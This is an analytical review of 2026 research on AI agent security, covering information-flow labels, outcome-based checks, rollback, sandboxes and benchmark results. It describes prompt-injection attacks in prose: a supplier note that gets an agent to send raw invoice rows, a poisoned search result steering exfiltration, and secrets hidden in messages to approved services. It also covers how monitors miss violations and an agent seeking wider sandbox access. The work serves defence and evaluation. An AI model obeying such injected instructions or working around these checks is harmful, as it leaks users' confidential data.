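*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send the auditor only the totals. A hidden instruction in a supplier's note leads the agent to save the individual invoice rows in a file, `report.csv`, and request approval to send it to the auditor. The policy allows the tool, the auditor is an approved recipient, and the file name looks ordinary. A bound approval would not help, because the file sent is exactly the one the user approved.

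Sensitivity labels are meant to catch this. In Parallax, the executor labels data as public, internal, confidential or restricted when it reads the data, based on the file's location, patterns in the content and project rules. If the agent later asks to write or send something derived from that data, the request inherits the label. Parallax blocks restricted content from going to any destination the network can reach, no matter how many steps separate the read from the send.

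Hossain and colleagues track the origin of each file instead. If an agent writes a file z′ after reading z₁ to zₖ, the system assumes that z′ may contain something from all of them:

L(z′) ⊇ L(z₁) ∪ … ∪ L(zₖ)

L(z) is the set of sources behind z. Since the raw rows are among the sources of `report.csv`, the system can compare the request to send it with the user's original restriction. It returns "allowed", "violation" or, if the record is incomplete, "unknown". In the tests, a gate blocked both violations and unknowns:

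| Agent's model | Gate | Attack runs with an unauthorised effect | Harmless runs completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | Off | 52 of 120 | 104 of 120 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | On | 6 of 120 | 100 of 120 |
| Qwen3 8B | Off | 58 of 120 | 110 of 120 |
| Qwen3 8B | On | 7 of 120 | 106 of 120 |

Both models are small, and the runs repeat 24 attack scenarios with variations. A separate test shows more about why the gate works. The monitor detected 69 of 80 violations that depended on earlier steps, but only 16 when the researchers removed its memory of those steps. When parts of the record were missing, it detected 51, and the agent completed only 76.7% of harmless tasks because the gate blocked so many unknown cases.

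The same record can help a person decide whether to approve a request. Hossain and colleagues had 80 volunteers judge requests on one of four screens. Those who saw a short description of the next action approved 55.0% of the unsafe requests. Those who saw the user's original restriction and a full log approved 32.5%, and those whose screen also stated the combined effect ("The attachment was built from raw invoice rows") approved 24.2%. The difference between the last two could be due to chance, so most of the demonstrated benefit comes from showing the history.

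### Where labels get lost, and where they spread too far

Labels work well while ordinary code copies data from place to place. They become unreliable when the data passes through a language model. Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, describe three ways in which this happens:

- Paraphrase. An agent rewrites a confidential patient note in its own words, and no phrase of the original survives for a program to match.
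- Influence without copying. A poisoned search result persuades the agent to send its research to an attacker's website. The request need not contain any text from the search result, which affected only the choice of tool.
- Memory. An agent stores a confidential sales forecast on one day and uses it in a report three days later. If the memory store does not save the label with the text, the second session treats the forecast as ordinary data.

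Cai and colleagues built a tool that looks for all three. On their own set of 400 scenarios, it scored 0.928 on F1, a measure that combines missed cases and false alarms, where 1 is perfect. FIDES, an existing label-based system, scored 0.522. The tool examines the agent's log afterwards, so it can report a leaked forecast to the owner but cannot prevent the leak. Labels can also be missing from the start, as in Parallax, where sensitive text that matches no rule gets no suitable label.

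The cautious alternative is to give everything the model produces the labels of everything it has read. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) explains that every piece of data soon carries every label, so the labels no longer distinguish anything. On the web server, once the model had read a confidential customer complaint, even the number 20 in its next request would count as confidential.

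Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated how far such labels spread among groups of agents. Restricting sensitive tools to a few agents reduced the spread, as did letting agents communicate directly instead of through intermediaries. No arrangement prevented it, so labels that no longer apply still have to be removed. *Sightline* (2026) estimates which inputs actually affected an output. On one agent, its method removed 50.0% of the unnecessary labels but had misses in 3.9% of episodes, and an attacker who can try repeatedly might find one.

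### Judging the result instead of the call

Another approach is to check the state that would result from the next action, given everything the agent has already done. For example, three small payments may each be acceptable but together exceed the daily budget.

One developer compared this approach with ordinary checks in a pilot of 24 runs, using simulated email, server, code and payment services. Four attacks and four similar legitimate tasks each ran under three policies: no check, a check on each call alone, and a check on the resulting state. With no check, all four attacks reached the forbidden result. With the check on each call, three did, and the model abandoned the fourth without being blocked, so the check stopped none of them. With the check on the resulting state, no attack succeeded. The agent completed all the legitimate tasks under every policy.

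Four attacks are too few to estimate how often the check works. A check that missed half of all such attacks would still stop all four in about one pilot out of 16. The developer also designed the attacks and the rules that stopped them. The pilot shows little more than that the idea can work on chosen examples.

*Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) reports a larger test, in which an agent shared calendar information and the user had consented to only a limited total. With no guard, an agent running Qwen3-30B exceeded that limit in 22 of 60 runs. With a guard that compared each action with the task's purpose, it exceeded the limit in 20 of 60. With a guard that added up what the agent had already disclosed, it never exceeded the limit, and that guard blocked nothing in 120 harmless runs. An agent running Gemma-4 never exceeded the limit, even without a guard, so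 the size of the benefit depends on the model.

Pandey and colleagues also prove that some violations are invisible in any single run. Suppose a scheduling assistant may reveal when its user is busy but not why. In one run, the busy time is an ordinary meeting, and the assistant offers slot 10. In another, it is a confidential job interview, and the assistant offers slot 11. Both offers are acceptable, but the difference between them depends on the secret. The rule that the assistant breaks compares two runs, t and t′:

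low(t) = low(t′) and D(hi(t)) = D(hi(t′)) ⇒ α(obs(t)) = α(obs(t′))

Here low is the request and other ordinary input, hi is the private context, and D selects the part of that context the assistant may use. The assistant's message is obs, and α selects the parts of it that matter to the policy. In words, if the request and the permitted information are the same, the disclosure must be the same.

No single run can break this rule, so a monitor that checks runs one at a time either raises false alarms or misses every violation. Labels don't help either, because the message contains no secret text. An executor can still prevent the problem by offering an operation that returns only free and busy times, so that the model process never receives the reasons for them.

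The defenders' reply does not excuse the invoice case, because the user said "summary totals only" and nobody had authorised sending the rows. The check looked at only one step and failed at the job the pattern is supposed to do. The reply is sound when the owner never stated the restriction. *Agenra* (2026) describes a monitor that tracks earlier calls and has a core with computer-checked proofs, but even that monitor cannot enforce a rule missing from its policy.

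### Mistakes that the owner can undo

A permitted operation can do harm without an attacker or a broken rule, as when the model writes 200 megabytes instead of 20 and the owner approves it. Such errors are common in ordinary work. Santos-Grueiro reviewed 40 tasks that had passed every authority check and found that 11 still needed a person's attention, for reasons such as missing tests.

Saving the old state makes many of these errors easy to undo. Before Parallax overwrites or deletes a file, its Chronicle component copies the file's contents and metadata. Chronicle names each copy by its SHA-256 digest and links it to the action that caused the change. The owner can restore the file with one command, and the agent cannot alter the copies. By default, Chronicle keeps at most 100 copies, for up to 30 days. An agent that makes many small edits could presumably cause Chronicle to delete the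 copy that the owner needs.

Restoring `shop.conf` corrects the upload limit completely. It also stops the forwarding of the checkout page, but it does not retrieve the card details that customers sent in the meantime. Fokou accepts that Chronicle cannot reverse sent emails, published messages or calls to outside services. *Revisable by Design* (2026) sorts actions into four kinds, which on the web server might look like this:

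| Kind of action | Example | Remedy |
|---|---|---|
| Changes nothing | Read the error log | None needed |
| Reversible | Replace `shop.conf` | Restore the saved copy |
| Compensable | Email customers the wrong upload limit | Send a correction |
| Irreversible | Send card details to a stranger | None that recovers the secret |

Restoring only the local files can erase the record of changes an agent made elsewhere. *Planarian* (Guo, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that corrects records in a remote database and writes a local report of its changes. If the owner restores only the local files, the report disappears but the database changes remain.

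Planarian reverses both. It takes snapshots of the agent's sandbox, including running programs, and keeps a list of actions that would undo each remote change. For a database, it saves the affected rows before changing them and records which rows the change touched, all in one transaction. To go back, it applies the undo actions in reverse order and then restores the sandbox. It refuses any remote request it cannot undo. Planarian added only 1% to 3% to the time that administration tasks took. However, the prototype can undo remote changes only in SQL databases, and it assumes that nobody else is changing the same data. In a live shop, customers place orders while the agent works, so restoring an old row could erase a newer change.

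What the owner has undone may also still affect the model. To save time, the server that runs a model keeps intermediate results from text it has already processed. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) cites an audit in which stored results from an abandoned attempt changed a protected decision in 25 of 63 cases, although the abandoned text was no longer in the request. Rebuilding the stored results fixed every case.

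*Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of 435 works on agents that keep running, found a rollback mechanism in only 27. If an action can't be undone, the safeguards have to come before it. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) requires the policy to authorise such actions explicitly. *POLAR* (2026) describes a system that works out the recovery steps in advance, so that an approver can inspect them before the action runs. An executor can also hold outgoing messages for a few minutes so that a person or a validator can cancel them.

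For honest mistakes, the defenders are right that the owner had the authority to choose 200 and used it, but that doesn't help an owner whose disk is full. Saved copies help more, but only the owner should be able to restore them, as in Parallax. If a hijacked model process could restore old files, it might bring back a configuration with a security hole that the owner had since closed.

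## How much does the pattern stop, and at what cost?

Jing's benchmark tests typed operations, a fixed policy, approvals, a log and a sandbox in one system. It contains 313 cases:

- 54 ordinary tasks, which the system should allow;
- 74 openly dangerous operations;
- 122 disguised operations, in 15 families such as short file names, links and commands assembled from fragments;
- 31 attacks on actions after approval;
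- 32 faults, such as a missing policy or a log that the system cannot write to.

Jing fixed the list and the correct verdicts in advance, then compared eight versions of the system, from no protection to the full design with a sandbox. Five of the disguised commands cannot run in any version because the Windows shell does not recognise them, so the success rates cover the other 117. As in the earlier test of models with only a prompt to restrain them, a request for approval counts as permission. The main results cover six of the versions:

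| Version | Disguised attacks let through | Ordinary tasks refused |
|---|---|---|
| Direct execution, no checks | 115 of 117 (98.3%) | None |
| Text filter on commands | 51 of 117 (43.6%) | None |
| Typed operations only | 4 of 18 (22.2%) | None |
| Full design, no sandbox | 36 of 117 (30.8%) | None |
| Full design with a check of the file's bytes | 36 of 117 (30.8%) | None |
| The same, with a sandbox | 9 of 117 (7.7%) | 6 of 54 (11.1%) |

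The text filter stopped 64 attacks with disguised commands that direct execution had let through. The rest of the design stopped another 15, and the sandbox another 27. The filter and the sandbox, both of which are common without this pattern, therefore accounted for 91 of the 106 attacks stopped. The pattern's own parts matter more once somebody has approved an action. The text filter blocked only 2 of the 27 attacks on approved actions that it could receive, while the full design with the byte check blocked 28 of 31.

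Typed operations alone seem to do better than the full design, but only 18 of the attacks could take the form of a typed operation. With so few cases, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 45%, and those 18 attacks may be easier or harder to stop than the other 99, so the result does not show that typed operations are safer. The main argument for them is still that the checker has much less to work out.

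The 7.7% also excludes the openly dangerous operations. Jing reports that the version with the sandbox wrongly allowed 23.0% of these, which corresponds to 17 of the 74. Obvious attacks therefore succeeded more often than disguised ones, which seems odd, but the counting rule may explain part of the difference. A policy that sends an obvious deletion to a person for approval counts as having allowed it, so the rate could be much lower with an attentive owner.

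Nor did the system always fail closed. It did so in 87.5% of the fault cases, or 28 of 32.

### What the sandbox contributes

The 7.7% depends on assumptions about what the sandbox would block, because Jing did not run all 117 attacks against a real one. To check these assumptions, Jing ran 94 of the disguised commands in a copy of the system. Of these, 28 gave no useful information about the sandbox: the model refused to run five, ten did not work in the copy, eleven ran without effect and two had unclear results. Of the other 66, the system blocked 61 and five took effect (7.6%).

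The close match between 7.6% and 7.7% is mostly luck. Under the assumptions, five of the 94 commands should have taken effect. Five did in the real runs, but they were a different five. The real runs therefore support the rough size of the figure but not the predictions for particular attacks.

Only one of the five successful commands escaped the sandbox, through the gap that let it delete a file on another drive. Three others deleted files inside the agent's own workspace, where the sandbox permits changes. Leftover files from the agent made the remaining result unreliable.

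In a second, more direct test of the sandbox's contribution, Jing ran 88 of the commands with the sandbox on and again with it off. Switching it off let 45 commands run that the system had previously stopped, and it stopped none that had previously run. The same switch also turned off approval requests, but missing approvals had caused only four refusals in the real runs, so the sandbox probably caused most of the difference.

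In the first test without the sandbox, two commands reached Jing's live system through a network path and deleted a protected file. Jing restored the file and repeated the experiment, leaving out six commands that still pointed at the live system.

An executor that accepts shell commands but has no sandbox should therefore have an attack success rate closer to 30.8% than to 7.7%. The first rate is four times the second. The attacks that only the sandbox stopped included paths written with forward slashes, old-style short names, links, and Python programs that wrote to files directly.

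In Jing's system, the sandbox can refuse an action that the policy has already allowed. A sandbox around the model process alone could not do this, because the executor acts with its own powers. The owner of the web server should confine the executor too, so that it can write only to the site configuration directory and restart only nginx. If the path check then misses a link to the password file, the operating system still refuses the write.

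An agent that is allowed to request wider access can weaken its sandbox from inside. In one run, the agent made such a request unprompted after the sandbox refused an operation. The request failed because nobody was there to approve it. Jing did not test what happens when a person is available to approve.

### Parallax's 280 attacks

Fokou sent 280 attacks straight to Parallax's checks, including injected instructions, disguised commands, chains of tool calls and attempts to disable the checks. With its default settings, Parallax blocked 277 of them and refused none of 50 legitimate actions. With the classifier switched on for every type of action, it blocked all 280 but refused 18 of the 50 legitimate actions (36%).

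All three attacks that succeeded under the default settings got past the language model that acts as judge. It allowed the `env` command, the deletion of a temporary file, and a request to a web address that looked like a validation service. Without information about the task, the judge had little chance of identifying these as attacks.

Fokou also reports which tier decided each case:

| Tier | Attacks decided | Median delay |
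|---|---|---|
| Fixed policy | 43 | Under 1 millisecond |
| Patterns and classifier | 163 | 1.9 seconds |
| Model as judge | 73 | 2.1 seconds |
| Person | 1 | 2.5 seconds, with a simulated person who answers at once |

The paper describes these counts as blocked attacks. They add up to 280, which suggests that they come from the run with strict settings. But OpenParallax's *Methodology*, part of the documentation for Parallax's open-source software, gives the same counts for the default run, in which Parallax blocked only 277 attacks. The table therefore shows where Parallax decided each case, including the three attacks that the judge wrongly allowed out of the 73 it decided.

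The fixed policy decided only 15.4% of the attacks. Fokou adds the second tier's share and concludes that deterministic mechanisms handled 73.6%. Calling the second tier deterministic is generous, because it includes the classifier, a trained model that can fail on attacks unlike its training examples.

In one run recorded in OpenParallax's *Run History*, Fokou switched off that classifier and relied on the fixed patterns. Between 92% and 100% of attacks then succeeded in three categories: disguised commands, chains of tool calls and attacks through other agents. The current version sends more actions to the judge, so it might block more attacks without the classifier than that run did. Even so, an owner who never installs the classifier should not count on blocking 98.9% of attacks.

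According to the history, the default settings reached that figure over ten runs, as Fokou adjusted the rules and checks and retested them, largely on the same attacks. Some adjustments made the results worse. A rule that allowed every write to the workspace let more attacks through, and a change to the classifier raised the share of legitimate actions refused from 24% to 66%.

This is a reasonable way to develop a policy, but the results overstate how well it works, because rules fitted to known attacks usually do worse on new ones. The first run, before the adjustments, may better show how a new kind of attack would fare. In that run, 19.2% of attacks on the checks themselves succeeded, as did 4% of direct injections and 2.5% of indirect ones.

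Even repeating the same test can give a different result, because the judge does not always return the same verdict. OpenParallax's *Reproducing Run-013*, a guide to repeating the default run, allows a difference of two percentage points in the overall rate. It also gives zero as the expected number of successful attacks in the first seven categories, which contradicts the paper, where two of the three misses are in those categories.

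### What "no escapes" means

Santos-Grueiro observed no escapes in the 400 coding tasks, of which Context-to-Execution Integrity safely completed 231. An escape is an action that runs even though the policy did not authorise one of its protected fields, its effect or the run itself. The absence of escapes is good evidence that the system enforced its policy in these tasks, but weak evidence about whether another owner's policy would be good.

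The system also allowed 204 actions on AgentDojo, again with no observed escapes. Santos-Grueiro then ran 20 constructed attacks against the full system and against versions with only some of its checks. The partial versions rejected 8, 10 or 12 of the attacks, while the full system rejected all 20 and still allowed six legitimate actions. The perfect score is unsurprising because the attacks target the gaps that the full system closes. The comparison is more useful as evidence that a designer cannot safely leave out any one of the checks.

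Santos-Grueiro tested 192 cases in which a model read untrusted text and proposed an action. With no required format, the model used a malicious tool or destination every time. With a required format but no further checks, it never did, but untrusted text determined the value of a protected field in every case, so all 192 still counted as unauthorised. An owner would find a valid site name copied from the error log much less alarming than a request to run an attacker's program, but it may still be the wrong site.

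The same work offers some support for prompts as an additional safeguard. In one test, models with downloadable weights chose an unauthorised action in 196 of 300 cases. When the prompt explained the rules for each field, the number fell to 67. For models that companies run on their own servers, it fell from 85 of 400 to zero. A good prompt can evidently reduce how many requests the executor has to refuse, though 67 unauthorised requests would still have reached it.

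The zero that Safin and colleagues report for their chain of agents is weaker evidence because they copied their main policy from the answer key. They wrote a second policy by hand, but it matched the key on all 60 tasks, so it made the test no harder. They ran the main comparisons three times, for 180 trials per setting, but repeating the same 60 tasks with the same language model provides less evidence than 180 different tasks would.

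### Legitimate work refused

In Jing's benchmark, the policy refused none of the 54 ordinary tasks, and all six refusals came from the sandbox. The initial count was 11, but it included five commands that were wrongly assumed to write files. They only read files, and the real sandbox allows them.

Most of the trouble came from a mismatch between the directories the policy allows and those the sandbox allows. The policy allows the agent to write in its workspace and in the folder for temporary files, while the sandbox allows writes only in the session's working directory. The operating system can therefore refuse to create a temporary file that the policy allowed. This confuses the owner, whose log shows that the policy allowed the action, and the agent, which may keep trying. Giving the policy and the sandbox the same list of directories should prevent most such refusals.

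One refusal in nine tasks would annoy most people and may lead an owner to switch the sandbox off. However, with only 54 tasks tested, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 5% to 22%. Parallax's zero is also uncertain, because a system that refused 6% of legitimate actions would still show no refusals in about one of every 22 tests of 50 actions.

Stricter sandboxes can block much more legitimate work. In *Where Agent Defenses Fail*, Singh and Srinivasa (2026) tested a coding agent in two sets of 110 and 300 runs, with tasks that included uploading a status report. When a strict sandbox cut off the network, they observed no harm from attacks, but the agent completed only 6 of 8 legitimate tasks in one set and 12 of 24 in the other.

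Singh and Srinivasa then added a program outside the sandbox that sent approved requests for the agent, much as an executor would. The uploads worked again, but so did attacks that hid a secret in a message to the approved service. A further check blocked messages that contained a complete line from the secrets file. It did not interfere with any legitimate task, but two attacks got past it by sending the secret value without the rest of its line.

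The executor in this experiment removed some of the protection the sandbox had provided. The same could happen on the web server if the owner added an operation for sending reports to the hosting company. Checking the destination address would not be enough, because a hijacked model process could put the shop's database password in the report.

### Delay and other running costs

Checking actions against fixed rules adds little delay. Fatmi reports that on one Apple M1 workstation, half of Faramesh's decisions took at most 2.24 milliseconds and 95% took at most 9.61 milliseconds. These times include converting the request to canonical form, checking the policy and recording the decision. An agent that takes several seconds to choose its next step would not be noticeably slower.

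Checks that use a trained model are slower, at about two seconds each in Parallax. The delay hardly matters for the upload limit, since that change waits for the owner anyway, but it adds ten minutes when an agent edits 300 files. The developers attribute the classifier's delay to the way the program loads it and expect a replacement to take about 30 milliseconds. The judge would remain slow because it calls an outside service.

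Context-to-Execution Integrity can be slower still with a hosted model. It uses separate calls to read untrusted text and to fill in the protected fields, and full requests on AgentDojo took between 9 and 15 seconds. Santos-Grueiro reports that the policies for 24 tools and other endpoints cover 149 fields and needed 141 tests of the code that validates their values. Somebody has to maintain the policies and tests as the tools change.

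A growing log can slow down even a simple executor. Jing's system took 4 to 6 milliseconds with an empty log. But it searched the whole log to check an approval, and at 50,000 lines it took 164 milliseconds to find a recent entry and 676 to find the oldest. A system that makes a few hundred decisions a day reaches that size in a month or two.

Jing changed the search to start from the newest entry, which cut the time to find a recent approval to 0.83 milliseconds. Finding the oldest entry still took 228 milliseconds. An attacker could keep the executor busy searching by repeatedly presenting very old approvals. An index, which lets a program find an entry without reading the others, would be better.

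Fixed rules cost less to run because they need no calls to a language model. When Jing asked models to make the decisions instead, each attempt cost $0.22 on average, although the most expensive model cost about 400 times as much as the cheapest.

### Records lost when programs write together

Jing's main benchmark ran one action at a time, and the full design recorded every decision, execution and result. The log lost entries only when several programs wrote to it at the same time. It lost about a tenth with two programs, over a fifth with four and almost a third with eight. The tests also left 12 damaged lines, which the software skipped without warning when it read the log.

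An owner could run such a system for months without noticing the gap. A single agent on the web server might never cause it, but several helper agents working at once could. The missing entry might have been the only record of who changed the payment site.

After adding the lock, Jing found no missing entries in five repetitions with one, two, four and eight programs. The lock slows writes, but this is acceptable because the executor relies on the log. Jing also recommends a separate check that counts damaged lines, so that the owner finds out when the log is incomplete.

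### Who ran the tests, and what they counted

Jing, Fokou, Fatmi and Santos-Grueiro each tested their own system, mostly with attacks they chose themselves. This doesn't make their results wrong, but people tend to test for problems they have already thought of. An outsider with a week to break the web server's executor would probably find problems they missed.

The settings were narrow too. Jing used one Windows computer and one version of its shell, so the results for short file names and drives may not carry over to a Linux server. The longest runs lasted about a day, too short to show how owners change their policies after months of interruptions.

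Jing describes six measurement mistakes that at first produced plausible but wrong results. In one, the harmful commands never reached the agent. In another, the test program mistook ordinary words in a reply for refusals. This openness is unusual and makes the corrected figures more credible, but similar mistakes may remain in tests whose authors report none.

The percentages also can't be used to rank the systems, because neither author ran the other's test cases. Fokou's Parallax let through 1.1% of a mix of plain and disguised attacks, while Jing's system let through 7.7% of a set made up only of disguised ones.

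A public benchmark such as AgentDojo makes comparison easier, but its scores can also mislead. *NOMOS* (2026) describes a system that turns written policies into checks on tool calls, and it compares AgentDojo's scores with the actions that ran. On the messaging tasks, an agent using a Llama model had a reported attack success rate of 10.5%, although no malicious action ran. AgentDojo had counted as successes some attempts that the checks blocked and some attacks that aimed only to make the agent write something.

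AgentDojo also scored some attacks as unsuccessful even though they did real harm. On the banking tasks, injected instructions led to payments to people the user already paid, and in nine of the office cases the agent deleted things on the attacker's orders.

Singh and Srinivasa deal with this by examining the saved files and the messages the outside service received, rather than relying on the log of the system under test. The owner of the web server could test an executor the same way, by sending it a harmful request and then checking the configuration files and outgoing traffic to see what changed.
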